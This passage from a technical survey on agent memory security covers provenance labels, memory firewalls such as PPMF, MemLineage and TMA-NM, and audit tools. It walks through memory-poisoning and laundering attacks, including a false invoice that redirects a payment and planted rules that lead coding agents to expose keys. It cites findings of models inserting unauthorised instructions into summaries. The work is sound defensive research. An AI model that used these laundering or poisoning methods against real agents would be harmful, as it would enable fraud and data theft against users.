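Memory software that replaces an old fact with a newer one gives the last writer control of the result. As in polyinstantiated databases, the software can make the label part of the key, so that "Acme's account number, from the user" and "Acme's account number, from email" are separate entries. An email can then update only the second. Deduplication also needs to keep the two entries separate when they match. Merging them would produce one entry with an untrusted label, so an attacker could make the agent lose its trusted copy of the number by repeating it.

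#### Expose narrow views

A planner often needs only a small part of a memory. To schedule a meeting, for example, it needs the free hours in a calendar but not the appointment titles. A declassifying view can return just the hours, so the private titles don't enter the planner's context or affect its label.

A developer should write such views, rather than the planner, because their author decides what becomes public. If a model wrote its own views while an attacker's text was in its context, the attacker could instruct it to write one that exposed everything. Developers should also write views that raise trust, which amount to endorsement.

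### Where the comparison fails

A database copies values exactly. When a program copies an account number from one row to another, the software can identify the row it came from. The label rules rely on software being able to trace each output to its inputs.

A language model gives the software no record of which inputs shaped its output. If a planner reads ten memories and writes one sentence, any of the ten may have influenced it, including those whose words do not appear. To be safe, the software must give the sentence the combined label of everything in the context, which speeds up label creep. Labelling the sentence by the words it shares with the memories would miss paraphrases, and treating the model as its author would let untrusted content pass as trusted.

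Stored data also cannot change a well-built database query, whereas a planner that reads an attacker's words in a memory may change what it searches for next. Query by Label would still limit that search to rows the planner is allowed to see, but the attacker could choose what the agent looks for within them.

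## What happens to a label when a model summarises what it has read?

A summary is a new piece of data, so the software around the model has to decide which label it gets. If a model writes a note about an untrusted web page and the software files that note as the agent's own knowledge, or as something the user said, the untrusted label is lost but the page's content remains. This is called laundering, and it can happen whenever a trusted component rewrites, summarises or repeats untrusted content.

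Suppose on Monday the agent reads Acme's false invoice and saves the note "The user pays Acme by transfer to the account ending 4471". The stored note has no label and doesn't mention an invoice or an email. On Tuesday the planner reads what looks like one of the user's habits. An accurate summary that leaves out its source is enough to cause this, even if the model never obeys a hidden instruction.

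Many agents write their memories by condensing each session into a few short notes, a step called consolidation. A model can write unreliable notes even without an attacker. OpenAI's *Self-generated prompt injections in compaction summaries* (2026) describes rare cases in which a model in training added unauthorised instructions to the summaries it used to continue its tasks.

### How often summaries lose the source

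*Memory Provenance Laundering in LLM Agents* (Xu, Xiao et al., 2026) measures laundering with a two-task test. In Task A, the agent reads a web page, email or other outside material that an attacker controls, and a model summarises it into memory. In Task B, the agent retrieves that memory while working on a later request and may take a high-risk action, such as a purchase, that the user has not requested or confirmed. In one example, a web page recommends resuming a particular workflow in future tasks, and the model records the workflow as the user's own.

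The laundering rate is the share of malicious cases in which the stored memory presents outside content as the user's history, an established workflow or something like a confirmation. Attack success is the share in which the unauthorised action goes through in Task B. The researchers tried six open models as memory writers, on 30 malicious cases that they wrote themselves and 96 that they derived from AgentDojo:

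| Memory writer | Laundering, synthetic cases | Attack success, synthetic cases | Laundering, AgentDojo cases | Attack success, AgentDojo cases |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5 1.5B | 87% | 27% | 96% | 5% |
| Qwen2.5 3B | 87% | 87% | 99% | 8% |
| Qwen2.5 7B | 100% | 57% | 100% | 10% |
| Qwen2.5 14B | 100% | 93% | 100% | 49% |
| Llama 3 8B | 100% | 100% | 100% | 13% |
| Mistral 7B | 90% | 80% | 97% | 5% |

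On the AgentDojo cases, the models laundered between 95.8% and 100% of the memories, but most of the attacks failed. When the agent stored the raw material instead, every attack succeeded. Summarising made the attacks less effective but removed the evidence a later check would need. Among the Qwen models, attack success on these cases rose with model size, perhaps because a better summariser keeps more of the details the attacker's action requires.

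These were small models, and their prompt asked for a helpful memory but didn't ask them to keep track of sources. A different prompt might lower the laundering rates. Size alone does not seem to help. In 1,046 cases built from runs of the larger Llama 3.3 70B, every attack succeeded when the agent had no defence.

### Why text filters miss laundered notes

Xu and colleagues also tested filters that inspect stored notes before the agent uses them. One looked for phrases typical of prompt injection, such as commands to disregard earlier instructions. The summaries no longer contained such phrases, so this filter stopped nothing. With notes written by Qwen2.5 14B, attack success was 93% on the synthetic cases and 49% on the AgentDojo cases, with or without the filter.

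A broader filter blocked notes that mentioned links, payments, passwords or deletions. It cut attack success on the synthetic cases from 93% to 20%, but it also blocked half of the legitimate actions. It stopped none of the attacks in a harder set that used indirect references and split information across several places. Another test used a small purpose-built website and counted an attack only if it changed something on the server, for example by posting a review or deleting a file. There the filter cut attack success from 100% to 30% but blocked all five legitimate tasks.

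Both filters were simple keyword rules. A trained classifier might catch more disguised instructions, but a laundered note may contain nothing suspicious. "The user pays Acme by transfer to the account ending 4471" would read the same if the user had said it, so no classifier could tell the true version from the false one by its wording.

Another defence in the study inferred from a note's wording whether its content came from outside, the user's history or a confirmation. A strict version blocked every legitimate action, while a permissive one allowed 97.9% of them but also 98.4% of the attacks.

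Writing the source into the note did not solve the problem either, because a planner can read that a note came from a web page and still act on it. The researchers prompted the models to mention where information came from but let the agent act without any further check. On the synthetic cases, attacks succeeded 97% of the time with Qwen2.5 3B, compared with 87% for ordinary notes, and 100% of the time with Llama 3 for both kinds of note.

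### Matching a memory's authority to an action's risk

Xu and colleagues propose a defence called the Provenance-Preserving Memory Firewall (PPMF). Like MemLineage, it attaches a record of origin to each memory entry. The model writes the entry's text, and ordinary software fills in the record based on the channel the content came through.

The record gives each memory one of six levels of authority, which from lowest to highest are unknown, external, trusted tool, user history, user-confirmed and system. As with integrity labels, a claim in a memory, such as an account number, can have no more authority than its least authoritative source. Only an event that the software itself recorded, such as the user confirming that particular payee, can raise the level.

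Before each tool call, a gate compares the memory's level with the risk of the action:

| Type of action | Examples | Lowest level that can authorise it |
|---|---|---|
| Read | Search, open a page | External |
| Navigate | Open a saved workflow or an account page | User history |
| Outside effect | Post, send an email, delete a file | User-confirmed |
| Purchase | Check out, book, pay | User-confirmed |
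| Credential | Change a password | User-confirmed |

The gate finds the relevant memories without asking a model:

1. If the tool call names particular memory entries, the gate uses those.
2. Otherwise, it compares the call's targets, such as accounts, addresses and files, with the targets recorded for each retrieved memory.
3. If several memories match, it uses the level of the least trusted one.
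4. If the match is partial or missing, it treats every retrieved memory as relevant and again uses the lowest level.

Tuesday's payment needs a confirmed account number, and the one from the invoice is external, so the gate refuses the payment or asks the user to confirm the account. The agent can still read the note and answer questions about the invoice. A number that the user typed in March but never confirmed as a payee would count only as user history and would also need confirmation. If the attacker persuades the user to confirm the false account, the payment goes through. Xu and colleagues treat such attacks as out of scope for PPMF.

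This design largely avoids label creep, because an untrusted note about a holiday doesn't affect a payment whose target clearly matches another entry. FIDES, by contrast, would lower the trust level of the whole context as soon as the planner read the holiday note.

The drawback is that the gate checks what supports a call but ignores what caused it. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) make the same distinction in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, a survey of 71 works on tracing what agents do, and point out that a false memory can cause an action without supporting it. Suppose the user has confirmed Acme's real account, and a stranger's email leads the agent to note that Acme wants a second payment immediately. The account matches a recorded confirmation, so the gate could allow a payment that only the stranger wanted. FIDES would block it because the decision to pay came from an untrusted context.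 In the experiments, a confirmation was either present or absent. Xu and colleagues suggest adding limits on amount, time and scope, which would reduce this risk.

### What the gate depends on

With accurate records, PPMF let through no unauthorised high-risk action in any test. This mainly confirms that the software implements its rule correctly, regardless of how the model words its notes. The tests counted an attack as successful only if the agent took a high-risk action that the user had neither requested nor confirmed, and the gate is designed to refuse such actions.

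The more useful results come from damaging the records or hiding the right memory among others:

| Change | Attack success | Legitimate actions allowed |
|---|---|---|
| 20% of records lack a source | 0% | 81.4% |
| 10% of confirmations are forged | 8.8% | 100% |
| 10% of risky actions are mislabelled as read-only | 11.2% | 100% |
| 20 irrelevant memories added, agent retrieves 10 | 0% | 79.4% |
| 20 irrelevant memories added, agent retrieves 20 | 0% | 99.0% |

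When a record is missing, the gate treats the memory as unknown and blocks a legitimate action. The gate also refused the action when the agent failed to retrieve the confirmed memory, because nothing authorised it. Forged records let attacks through, and the attack success rate is close to the share of records that the attacker can forge.

PPMF's protection therefore holds only if the platform's own records are intact. The software must take the source from the channel the content arrived through, the confirmation from an actual click or similar event, and the risk from the tool's definition. Xu and colleagues recommend logs that software can add to but not alter. Few of the systems Wang and colleagues surveyed have any reported protection against tampering with their traces.

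The gate also needs records of origin made at the time of writing. On ordinary summaries, which had no such records, it blocked every attack but also nearly every legitimate action. Searching the summaries for signs of their source did not help, because the summariser had already removed those signs.

The study did not run CaMeL or FIDES for comparison. Most of its legitimate cases check whether confirmed actions pass the gate, and another 250 cover things like recalling a fact or reusing a preference. These cases do not show how well an agent with PPMF would complete whole tasks, or how soon users would tire of confirming actions.

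### When an agent edits its own memory files

The memory writers in these tests condensed whatever the agent had read. Coding assistants such as Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex can also keep memory in plain text files, which the agent must choose to edit. In *Bad Memory*, Gadgil, Alexander and colleagues (2026) found it difficult to use outside content to make these agents overwrite their memory files. They suggest that the agents treat the files as more privileged than other text. They tried this only in early exploration and give no success rates, so the finding is weak evidence that a determined attacker would fail. *InjecMEM* (2026) describes an attack on agent memory systems that needed only one interaction to steer later responses.

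Harmful text that was already in the files worked much better. An attacker might put it there through a security flaw, or a user might copy someone else's configuration file from a public forum. Gadgil and colleagues built a workspace for a fictional software engineer, planted one harmful rule in a file and gave the agent an ordinary task. The rules told the agent to add code that exposes a private key, install an outdated package with known security holes, or recommend a particular credit card. The table shows how often the agent complied in ten trials.

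| Model | Expose a private key | Install the package | Recommend the card |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 80% | 100% | 10% |
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 0% | 90% | 0% |
| GPT-5.2 | 30% | 0% | 40% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 80% | 100% |

Each rule was in a different file, so the columns aren't directly comparable. The numbers are also rough. A model that complies in none of ten trials could still have a true rate as high as about 26% at 95% confidence. Haiku exposed the key in 80% of these trials but in only 60% when the researchers repeated the first step in a longer experiment.

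In that longer experiment, the agent did the task, then an unrelated one, then a similar one. Haiku exposed the key 60% of the time in the first task and 100% in the last. It had written the key-reading code into a project file during the first task, and when it found that code in the last task, it was less suspicious of the rule. The agent's own work had laundered the attacker's instruction by making it part of the project's existing code.

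GPT-5.2 never installed the package, but it did not recognise the rule as an attack. In one case it copied the rule into the instructions file that Codex loads at the start of every session, which is the most trusted file in the workspace. The files have no labels, but a rule's location works like one, so moving the rule gave it more authority.

Refusing to follow a rule did not remove it from the file. Opus never exposed the key, but the key rule remained at the end of all ten longer sequences. When Opus noticed the credit card rule, it warned the user and offered to delete it, but the rule still survived in nine of ten sequences. Gadgil and colleagues point out that a user who nears their usage limit may switch to a weaker model, which could then follow the rule. The OpenAI models more often deleted the key rule and wrote a security rule in its place. The key rule survived in none of ten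 sequences with GPT-5.2 and two of ten with GPT-5.5.

Gadgil and colleagues recommend requiring explicit review of changes to important memory files, and letting low-trust files supply facts but not override safety rules. A gate like PPMF's could stop the agent from installing a package on the authority of an unlabelled file, but it would have no tool call to check if the agent recommended a credit card in an answer.

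### Reconstructing influence afterwards

NeuroTaint, the tracking software in *Ghost in the Agent*, looks for what caused an action after the agent has taken it. It reads the log of the agent's run, uses its saved records to connect sessions, and checks each sensitive tool call against the untrusted sources that could have reached it:

1. It adds a unique code to text from an untrusted source and checks whether the code appears in the tool call.
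2. It looks for fragments of the source that the agent copied.
3. It compares the meaning of the source with that of the call, using a model that turns sentences into lists of numbers. This can catch a paraphrase.
4. It repeats the comparison for small parts of the source, so that one harmful paragraph does not get lost in a long page.
5. If it finds no link, it asks a language model whether the agent would still have made the call if the source had contained neutral text.

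The last step covers text that influences an action without any of its words appearing in the result. For example, a false company policy might lead an agent to forward a customer's email to an attacker. The forwarded email contains nothing from the policy, but the agent would not have sent it otherwise. The judge's answer is only a model's prediction about another model's behaviour, and the judge also reads the original log, including the attacker's text.

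The researchers compared NeuroTaint with FIDES on TaintBench, a benchmark they built with 400 scenarios across 20 agent frameworks. In half of the scenarios, untrusted content influences a sensitive tool call. NeuroTaint had an F1 score of 0.928 and FIDES 0.522. F1 combines the share of alarms that are correct with the share of real cases found, and a perfect score is 1. The two systems scored almost the same on two existing benchmarks of unsafe agent behaviour, with 0.994 against 0.993 on the basic version of InjecAgent and 0.760 each on ToolEmu.

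The gap on TaintBench is weak evidence of which system protects an agent better. FIDES blocks actions that untrusted data might have influenced, whereas TaintBench tests whether the data did influence them. If an agent reads a web page and then writes a report that uses nothing from it, TaintBench counts an alarm as false. FIDES raised 106 such false alarms, but a system that cannot see inside the model keeps its guarantee by blocking reports like this.

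FIDES also missed 92 real cases. Some involved a second session that started without the labels from the first. Another 40 came from four frameworks where FIDES raised no alarms, which may reflect how the researchers connected it to those frameworks more than how it tracks data.

NeuroTaint missed 13 of the 200 real cases, and in ten of them repeated paraphrasing or delayed reuse had weakened the resemblance to the source. It did worst on scenarios built with the memory library Mem0, where it found seven of ten. Its similarity checks become less accurate the more often a model rewrites content, so an attacker's text is more likely to escape detection after several rounds of consolidation.

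The audit takes about a quarter of a second per step on average, but it runs after the agent has acted. On Tuesday evening it could show that the false invoice led to the payment, and its records could help the user find other memories from the same invoice, but the money would already be gone.

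## Can each memory carry its origin for good?

A reliable record of where a stored account number came from lets software block a payment. That record also has to carry over when agents write new memories from old ones. A note about Acme's invoice may go into a weekly summary, and the summary into a profile of the user's suppliers. Ding and colleagues set five requirements for stored state, two of which apply here: a memory's origin should stay on record through every change, and those changes should not increase its authority.

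Two designs from 2026 aim to meet these requirements. *MemLineage*, by Ouyang and Hou, estimates how much each old memory influenced a new one and ignores weak influences. Louck's *Securing LLM-Agent Long-Term Memory Against Poisoning* presents TMA-NM (Tamper-evident Memory Authority, Non-Malleable), which passes the untrusted label to everything derived from untrusted content, however weak the connection.

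### MemLineage

#### Signed entries

In MemLineage, each entry contains its text, its writer, a trust level, and links to the earlier entries that were in the model's context when it was written. The writer, which can be the user, the agent or a tool, signs the whole entry with a cryptographic key. If someone later edits the trust level in the database, the signature no longer matches and the software discards the entry. The software also records every entry and deletion in a log that it can add to but not alter, so an attacker can't remove an entry without leaving a trace.

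A signature shows who wrote an entry and that nobody has changed it since. It can't show whether the content is harmful, as *Threat Landscape of Vibe Coding and the Road to Secure Autonomy* (2026) points out about a similar format. When the agent summarises Acme's false invoice, it signs the summary with its own valid key, so only the links connect the summary to the invoice.

#### How trust passes along the links

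Trust levels run from 0 for trusted content, through 1 and 2 for content derived from trusted and untrusted sources, to 3 for outside content. A new entry $c$ with parents $P_c$ gets the level

$$\text{trust}(c) = \max_{p \in P_c}\ \mathbf{1}[w(p,c) > \tau] \cdot \text{trust}(p).$$

The weight $w(p,c)$, between 0 and 1, estimates how much parent $p$ influenced $c$, and $\tau$ is a threshold. The bracket equals 1 if the weight is above the threshold and 0 otherwise, so the new entry gets the worst level among the parents whose weights are above $\tau$.

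Suppose a note about Acme draws on a user message at level 0 and the emailed invoice at level 3. A scoring model weights these links at 0.8 and 0.4. With a threshold of 0.30, both links count, so the note gets level 3. With a threshold of 0.50, only the user's message counts, so the note gets level 0 and the agent may use it to justify a payment.

A link counts only if its weight is above the threshold. A link that counts passes on the parent's full level, whatever its weight, so the untrusted label does not fade gradually. Ouyang and Hou prove, one link at a time, that if every link on a path from an untrusted entry is above the threshold, the entry at the end is untrusted too.

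The guarantee is only as good as the weights. MemLineage can calculate them in three ways:

- It can give a weight of 1 to everything in the context.
- It can ask a second language model to score each parent's influence.
- It can read the writing model's internal attention values, which requires access to the model's weights. Ouyang and Hou have not yet tested this method.

A second model that scores influence has to read the attacker's text, so the text could manipulate the scores. MemLineage treats a new entry as trusted if no link is above the threshold, so an attacker who gets low scores for every parent gets a trusted memory. Developers can change this default to "untrusted", but that blocks more legitimate actions.

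#### Why the paper recommends a threshold of 0.10

Ouyang and Hou work through a case in which an untrusted source goes through a chain of rewrites. They assume that the scoring model gives the first link a weight of 0.9 and each later link 0.7 times the weight before it, so that

$$w_k = 0.9 \times 0.7^{\,k-1}.$$

| Link | 1 | 2 | 3 | 4 | 5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Weight | 0.900 | 0.630 | 0.441 | 0.309 | 0.216 |

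The untrusted label reaches the fifth rewrite only if the threshold is below 0.216. Ouyang and Hou give 0.10 as the limit for a chain of five because it was the highest threshold that worked among the few they tested (0, 0.10, 0.30, 0.50 and three values from 0.90 up). A threshold of 0.20 would also have worked.

A higher threshold makes the system less safe because it ignores more links. A developer who tested only one rewrite would conclude that 0.50 was safe, although it fails at the third. Even a threshold of 0.10 fails by the eighth rewrite, when the link's weight would be about 0.074. Under these assumptions, only a threshold of zero protects chains of every length.

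The falling weights are an assumption, because Ouyang and Hou scripted the scores instead of running a model. Each score compares an entry with its immediate parent, so there is no obvious reason for scores to fall as the chain grows. When the scripted weights did not fall, the length of the chain made no difference. But real scores would contain errors, which would accumulate with each rewrite. If a model missed 5% of links at random, the label would survive five rewrites only about 77% of the time.

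#### What the tests show

Ouyang and Hou's main test uses a simulated agent rather than a live language model and fixes the attacker's behaviour in advance, so each result is a single success or failure.

| Attack | No defence | Signatures only | MemLineage |
|---|---|---|---|
| The attacker's entry has no recognised signature | Succeeds | Blocked | Blocked |
| The attacker's text arrives by a legitimate route and the agent signs it | Succeeds | Succeeds | Blocked |
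| The agent writes and signs its own summary of the attacker's text | Succeeds | Succeeds | Blocked |

This confirms that the software applies its rules correctly, but not that it would stop an attacker who adapts. The test also gave every item in the context a weight of 1 and set the threshold to zero, so it in effect tested strict inheritance and not the scoring of influence.

Ouyang and Hou separately tested ways an attacker might get around the links. The attack succeeded if the agent saved a summary without recording its parent. With a threshold of 0.30, it also succeeded if the untrusted parent's weight was only 0.20, or if the text went through five rewrites with falling weights. Stricter settings blocked all three attacks. One of these settings refuses any sensitive action based on a memory with no recorded parents. It also blocked a legitimate email that the user had directly asked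 the agent to remember, because the user's own entry had no parents.

There were also small tests with live models. In one, an agent summarised an outside document in one session and recalled only the summary in the next. GPT-5.3-Codex took the attacker's action in 5 of 20 trials without a defence and in none with MemLineage, although the true rate with MemLineage could still be as high as 16%. GPT-5.2 never took the action, even without a defence.

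In another test, Ouyang and Hou combined three AgentDojo banking tasks with two attacks each and told the agent to trust tool output. The attacks succeeded in all six combinations without MemLineage and in none with it. When MemLineage replaced the attacker's values with values from a trusted bill, the agent completed the user's task in four of the six combinations, compared with two when MemLineage refused the call. AgentDojo has no persistent memory, and the researchers took the trusted bill from the benchmark's own answers. The test shows that the final check works if the labels are correct.

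### TMA-NM

#### Authority from the channel of arrival

When an item enters memory, TMA-NM assigns its origin based on the channel it came through, regardless of its content. An item from the user or a trusted tool can justify a consequential action. The agent's own notes can inform an answer but can't justify an action. Untrusted outside content and anything derived from it have no authority. Like the firewall that Xu and colleagues propose, TMA-NM keeps this record outside the model's control.

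The agent can still use an untrusted value if two independent trusted sources confirm it or the user approves that exact action. The approval covers one tool, recipient and amount, and works only once.

Louck identifies three ways to launder a memory, which the Acme invoice can illustrate:

- **Self-summarisation.** The agent reads the false invoice and writes a note in its own words that gives the account number. In TMA-NM, the note inherits the invoice's lack of authority.
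- **Trusted-tool echo.** The agent passes the false number to the company's accounting software, which repeats it in a draft payment. The number now seems to come from a trusted tool. TMA-NM treats a tool's output as untrusted if any of its inputs were untrusted.
- **Manufactured corroboration.** The attacker sends several emails with the same false number, so that the agent finds it in several places. TMA-NM counts only confirmations from trusted sources with separate identities and administrators and no shared source of data.

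#### The three theorems

Louck calls a defence malleable if laundering can raise a memory's authority without genuine approval. The theorems concern a small formal model of an agent that stores, rewrites and acts on memories:

1. A defence that judges memories by their content, or by links that depend on their content, is malleable. An attacker can reach a state in which an untrusted memory causes a consequential action.
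2. Without a record of origin from the time of writing, the attacker can reach such a state too.
3. With TMA-NM's rules, the attacker can't reach one.

A program called TLC checked these claims by going through every state the model can reach. The model has three memory slots, at most two sessions and a requirement of two confirmations. For the third theorem, TLC checked 3,270 states.

An agent has far more than three memories, so Louck extends the third theorem with an inductive invariant, a condition that stays true after any step if it was true before. TLC confirmed this for every step of the small model, including steps from states the agent could never reach. Louck then argues by hand that the invariant holds for any number of slots and sessions, because saving a memory fills only an empty slot, rewriting changes the text but not the origin, and an action goes ahead only if the safety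 condition holds. The argument is convincing for the model as described, but no software has checked it for an unlimited number of memories.

The formal model also assumes that a memory's origin stays correct when an attacker launders the memory by changing its text and links. Ensuring this is the hardest part in a real agent, where software has to work out the origin of each new note from whatever the language model read before writing it.

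The first theorem applies most clearly to links that a model scores by reading the text. If MemLineage instead gives every retrieved item a weight of 1, it takes the links from a record of what the agent retrieved, which rewording doesn't change.

#### The benchmark

Louck tested five kinds of defence with eight models from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google, Meta, DeepSeek and Alibaba. The scenarios included payments, purchases, settings changes and requests to send data. Each model had 24 runs for each kind of attack.

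| Defence | Direct attacks that succeed | Laundered attacks that succeed | Confirmed legitimate actions allowed | Unconfirmed legitimate actions taken without asking |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 84% | 68% | 100% | 100% |
| Judging the content | 0% | 68% | 100% | 100% |
| Links to sources | 0% | 47% | 100% | 0% |
| Single-session capabilities | 84% | 68% | 100% | 100% |
| TMA-NM | 0% | 0% | 100% | 0% |

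The "single-session capabilities" row measures Louck's stand-in for CaMeL and FIDES, not the systems themselves. The stand-in assumes that long-term memory is clean and approves every value recalled from it, so its results are identical to having no defence. They correspond to a CaMeL agent that treats all memory as trusted, and do not apply to one that restores each value's tag.

The "links to sources" row is also a stand-in, modelled on MemLineage. It approves an action if no link to an untrusted source remains, and Louck's self-summarisation attack removes the link. In a smaller test with three models, Louck changed the defence to refuse whenever a memory's origin was unclear. The success rate of self-summarisation attacks fell from 78% to 0%, but tool echoes still succeeded 74% of the time because the link to the tool was genuine. The stricter defence also refused every legitimate action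 whose origin was unclear.

TMA-NM's zeros follow largely from its rules, as they did for Xu and colleagues' firewall. The tests with real memory software are more informative. Louck connected TMA-NM to Mem0 and ran it with six models. Attacks succeeded in 50% of 96 runs without a defence and in none with TMA-NM. The agent completed 95 of 96 legitimate actions either way. Mem0 rewrites what it stores, but TMA-NM kept the origins in a separate record that Mem0 could not change.

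Louck also recreated the Trojan Hippo attack. It succeeded 78% of the time both without a defence and against the links defence, but never against TMA-NM.

TMA-NM does not prevent an untrusted memory from influencing what the agent tells the user. A false account number could still appear in an answer, and the user might then type it into a payment request.

### When the recorded origin is wrong

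Both designs depend on the software recording each memory's origin correctly. A wrong label is hard to fix later, because MemLineage's signatures protect wrong labels as well as correct ones, and every memory derived from the mislabeled one inherits the error.

Users can introduce errors by copying someone else's text into the chat. If a user pastes in an email from "Acme", both designs trust the text because it arrives through the user's own channel. The false account number then has the user's authority, and the attacker has not had to disguise its origin.

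Tools cause a similar problem. An authenticated connection to a mailbox proves that the mailbox is genuine, but not that the people who write to it are trustworthy. A developer who put the mailbox on TMA-NM's list of trusted tools would give authority to every stranger's email. *ClawMMU* (Hu, Mohammadi and colleagues, 2026) avoids this error by giving all tool output the lowest level of authority. The researchers have not yet built the design, which applies the idea of hardware memory protection to an agent's memory.

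An attacker could also take over a trusted tool. When Louck tested attacks in which one compromised source confirmed a false value, all of them failed because TMA-NM requires two confirmations. With two independent compromised sources, 67% of attacks succeeded. But TMA-NM requires confirmation only when an untrusted memory supports the value. If a compromised supplier registry provides the false account number, no untrusted memory is involved and the published procedure approves the payment immediately. Louck names a fully compromised tool as the main remaining risk.

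The software can also fail to record that a memory has an untrusted source. If the agent doesn't name a new entry's parents, MemLineage uses the results of the agent's most recent memory search as the parents. Suppose the agent reads the poisoned Acme note, then searches for the user's address, and then writes a summary. The Acme note is still in the model's context, but MemLineage would link the summary only to the address.

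TMA-NM has a related weakness, because it has to identify which memories a value came from. Louck points out that a model could assemble a value from pieces in several memories. One email might contain the first half of an account number and another the second half. If the software found no match for the full number in any untrusted memory, it would approve the payment. ClawMMU gives the lowest authority to any value it can't trace, so it would refuse the payment.

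ClawMMU can also revoke memories derived from a source that turns out to be bad. Every source has a counter, and each memory records the counter value of every source it came from. If the user reports that the invoice was forged, the software raises the invoice's counter from 0 to 1. A summary that recorded the counter as 0 then loses its authority the next time the agent retrieves it. Restoring an old backup can't undo this, because the software keeps the current counters outside the backups. According to Hu and colleagues, neither MemLineage nor TMA-NM can revoke derived memories in this way.

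### How far should an untrusted label spread?

Strict inheritance marks too many memories as untrusted, while weighted influence can miss the one that matters. Ameur, Mokhtari and Bouzefrane (2026) studied the same choice in *Forget the Lineage*. They wanted an agent that deletes a message to also delete everything derived from it, so they had to decide which memories descend from which sources.

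Their strict rule counts everything the model saw while writing a memory as a parent of that memory. They prove that, under this rule, a memory that does not descend from a source can't depend on that source's content. The proof assumes that the sources are independent of each other. For example, if the user repeats a door code in a second message, deleting the first does not remove the code. Their alternative rule keeps only the three parents closest in meaning to the new memory. It has no such guarantee, because the model might copy a detail from something else it saw.

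The strict rule has a serious drawback when the model reads a lot before writing, because a random deletion is more likely to hit one of a memory's source turns when the memory draws on more of them. Similarly, loading more memories makes it more likely that one is untrusted.

Deleting 1% of the turns erased 73.0% of derived memories when those memories were session summaries, which can depend on more than a hundred turns. When the model wrote each memory from only four turns, the same deletion erased 3.8%, and the agent answered questions better.

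The same calculation applies to untrusted labels. If one turn in a hundred, chosen at random, came from a stranger, strict inheritance would mark about three-quarters of the session summaries as untrusted. The real share would probably be lower, because emails and web pages tend to arrive in the same session. Writing notes from short passages would reduce this label creep without weakening the guarantee.

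Checking individual values also blocks fewer legitimate actions. Ouyang and Hou compared two rules on 13 legitimate actions in which trusted and untrusted material appeared in the same context. A rule that blocked sensitive actions whenever the context contained untrusted material allowed none of them. A rule that checked the source of each argument blocked every value the attacker supplied and still let nine of the actions complete. But a check on arguments, like Xu and colleagues' gate, doesn't control why the agent acts. Hu and colleagues acknowledge the same limit in their own design.

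Hu and colleagues apply the strictest inheritance. They treat the model as an untrusted source, so nothing it writes can justify an action until the user approves it. The software then doesn't have to estimate influence. However, even a number the user typed loses its authority once a model copies it into a note. An agent built this way should have ordinary software save the user's exact words.

*AgentKernel*, by Zou and colleagues, tries to give each memory the least restrictive label that its content allows. The software divides a conversation into segments with known sources and extracts possible memories from them. It finds the segments that support each memory, then searches for the least restrictive label that still accounts for the content within a set tolerance.

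Sometimes there is more than one such label. Suppose an email from the user's accountant and a web page both give Acme's office address. The email is trusted but secret, and the page is public but untrusted. Neither label is lower than the other, so the software keeps both.

Zou and colleagues acknowledge that an attacker could write text that blurs the boundaries between segments and so get a label that is too lenient. They give a security argument for the design but no experiments. Their method looks for the segments that support a memory, so it could also miss a segment that influenced which information the model recorded without supporting it.

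In case a label is wrong, AgentKernel limits which files and network addresses each tool can reach. This could stop a tool from sending stolen data to an unknown server. It would not stop Tuesday's payment, because a transfer to the attacker's account goes through the same bank server as a transfer to Acme.

Estimated influence is better suited to decisions where a mistake does little harm. *MAP-Graph* (2026), a design for memory shared by several agents, uses a memory's recorded ancestry to rank search results. It first excludes memories that the agent may not read, then multiplies each remaining memory's relevance by a trust score. An error there might put a poor result near the top of the list. With a payment, missing an influence could send money to the attacker, while an unnecessary untrusted label would usually mean the user has to confirm one more time.

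## Can a planner use a memory it is not allowed to read?

Even when software keeps an untrusted memory and its label intact, the agent still needs a safe way to use it. In the dual-LLM pattern, the planner refers to untrusted values by name without reading them. This works within one task because the planner created the names itself. But if an invoice is saved on Monday, a planner starting a new task on Tuesday did not create the name for it. That planner has to find out that the invoice exists and what it is, but reading the invoice would expose it to any instruction hidden inside.

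Girrens and Wang designed SPA for planners that need to use a memory they are not allowed to read. If the agent stores results on Monday, Tuesday's planner reads a short description of each one. Monday's planner wrote these descriptions before the agent had fetched anything.

### Three parts of a stored result

When a request finishes successfully, SPA saves the values that tools and the quarantined model produced. It splits each one into three parts, and a different component uses each part. For Monday's invoice they might look like this:

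| Part | Content for the Acme invoice | Component that uses it on Tuesday |
|---|---|---|
| Value | The invoice data, with the false account number and the hidden instruction | The interpreter, while it runs the plan |
| Label | Private, untrusted | The checker, before the plan runs |
| Description | "Details of the latest Acme invoice", the names and types of the fields, and a link to Monday's request | The planner |

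The planner has to annotate each step that calls a tool or the quarantined model with the step's purpose and the meaning of its result, and these annotations become the description. When it writes them, the planner has read only the user's requests, the list of tools and the descriptions of earlier results, so whoever sent the invoice cannot influence the wording. The sender could influence a summary, because a model writes it after reading the invoice.

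Tuesday's planner also sees the user's earlier requests, which lets it match "the invoice we discussed yesterday" to the right entry. SPA treats those requests as trusted. If the user pasted a stranger's email into Monday's request, Tuesday's planner would read the email too.

In SPA's standard mode, the planner reads the names, descriptions and data formats of the installed tools, where a malicious tool maker could also put instructions. SPA copies the tool's output format into the stored description, so the planner might still see such text after the user removes the tool. In an optional mode, the planner doesn't see the installed tools. A model first invents the tools that the request seems to need, and SPA tries to match them to real ones after planning. About three-quarters of runs in this mode failed at the matching step, so the results below are for the standard mode.

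### One plan, checked before it runs

SPA calls the planner once per request. The planner writes a complete plan in a small language with six kinds of step:

- **Retrieve** loads one stored result, which the plan must name.
- **Tool** calls an outside tool.
- **Quarantined model** extracts or condenses information from untrusted text.
- **Display** shows something to the user.
- **Condition** chooses between two branches.
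- **Loop** repeats some steps for each item in a list.

Because plans cannot do arithmetic, fill in text templates or define functions, software can work out which values each step depends on by reading the plan.

The checker goes through the plan in order, using labels but no values. It keeps a label $pc$, short for "program counter", for the circumstances in which the current step runs. This starts as the label of the user's request. The combined label of step $s$ is

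$$\ell(s) = pc \;\sqcup\; \bigsqcup_{x \in \text{inputs}(s)} \ell_x .$$

A tool step passes if $\ell(s)$ is no more confidential than the tool may receive and at least as trusted as the tool requires. The output of the quarantined model gets the label $\ell(s)$. A retrieve step restores the label that SPA saved with the value:

$$\ell_{\text{retrieved}} = \ell_{\text{stored}} \;\sqcup\; pc .$$

Inside a condition, the checker adds the label of the data being tested to $pc$ for both branches, because it cannot determine in advance which one will run.

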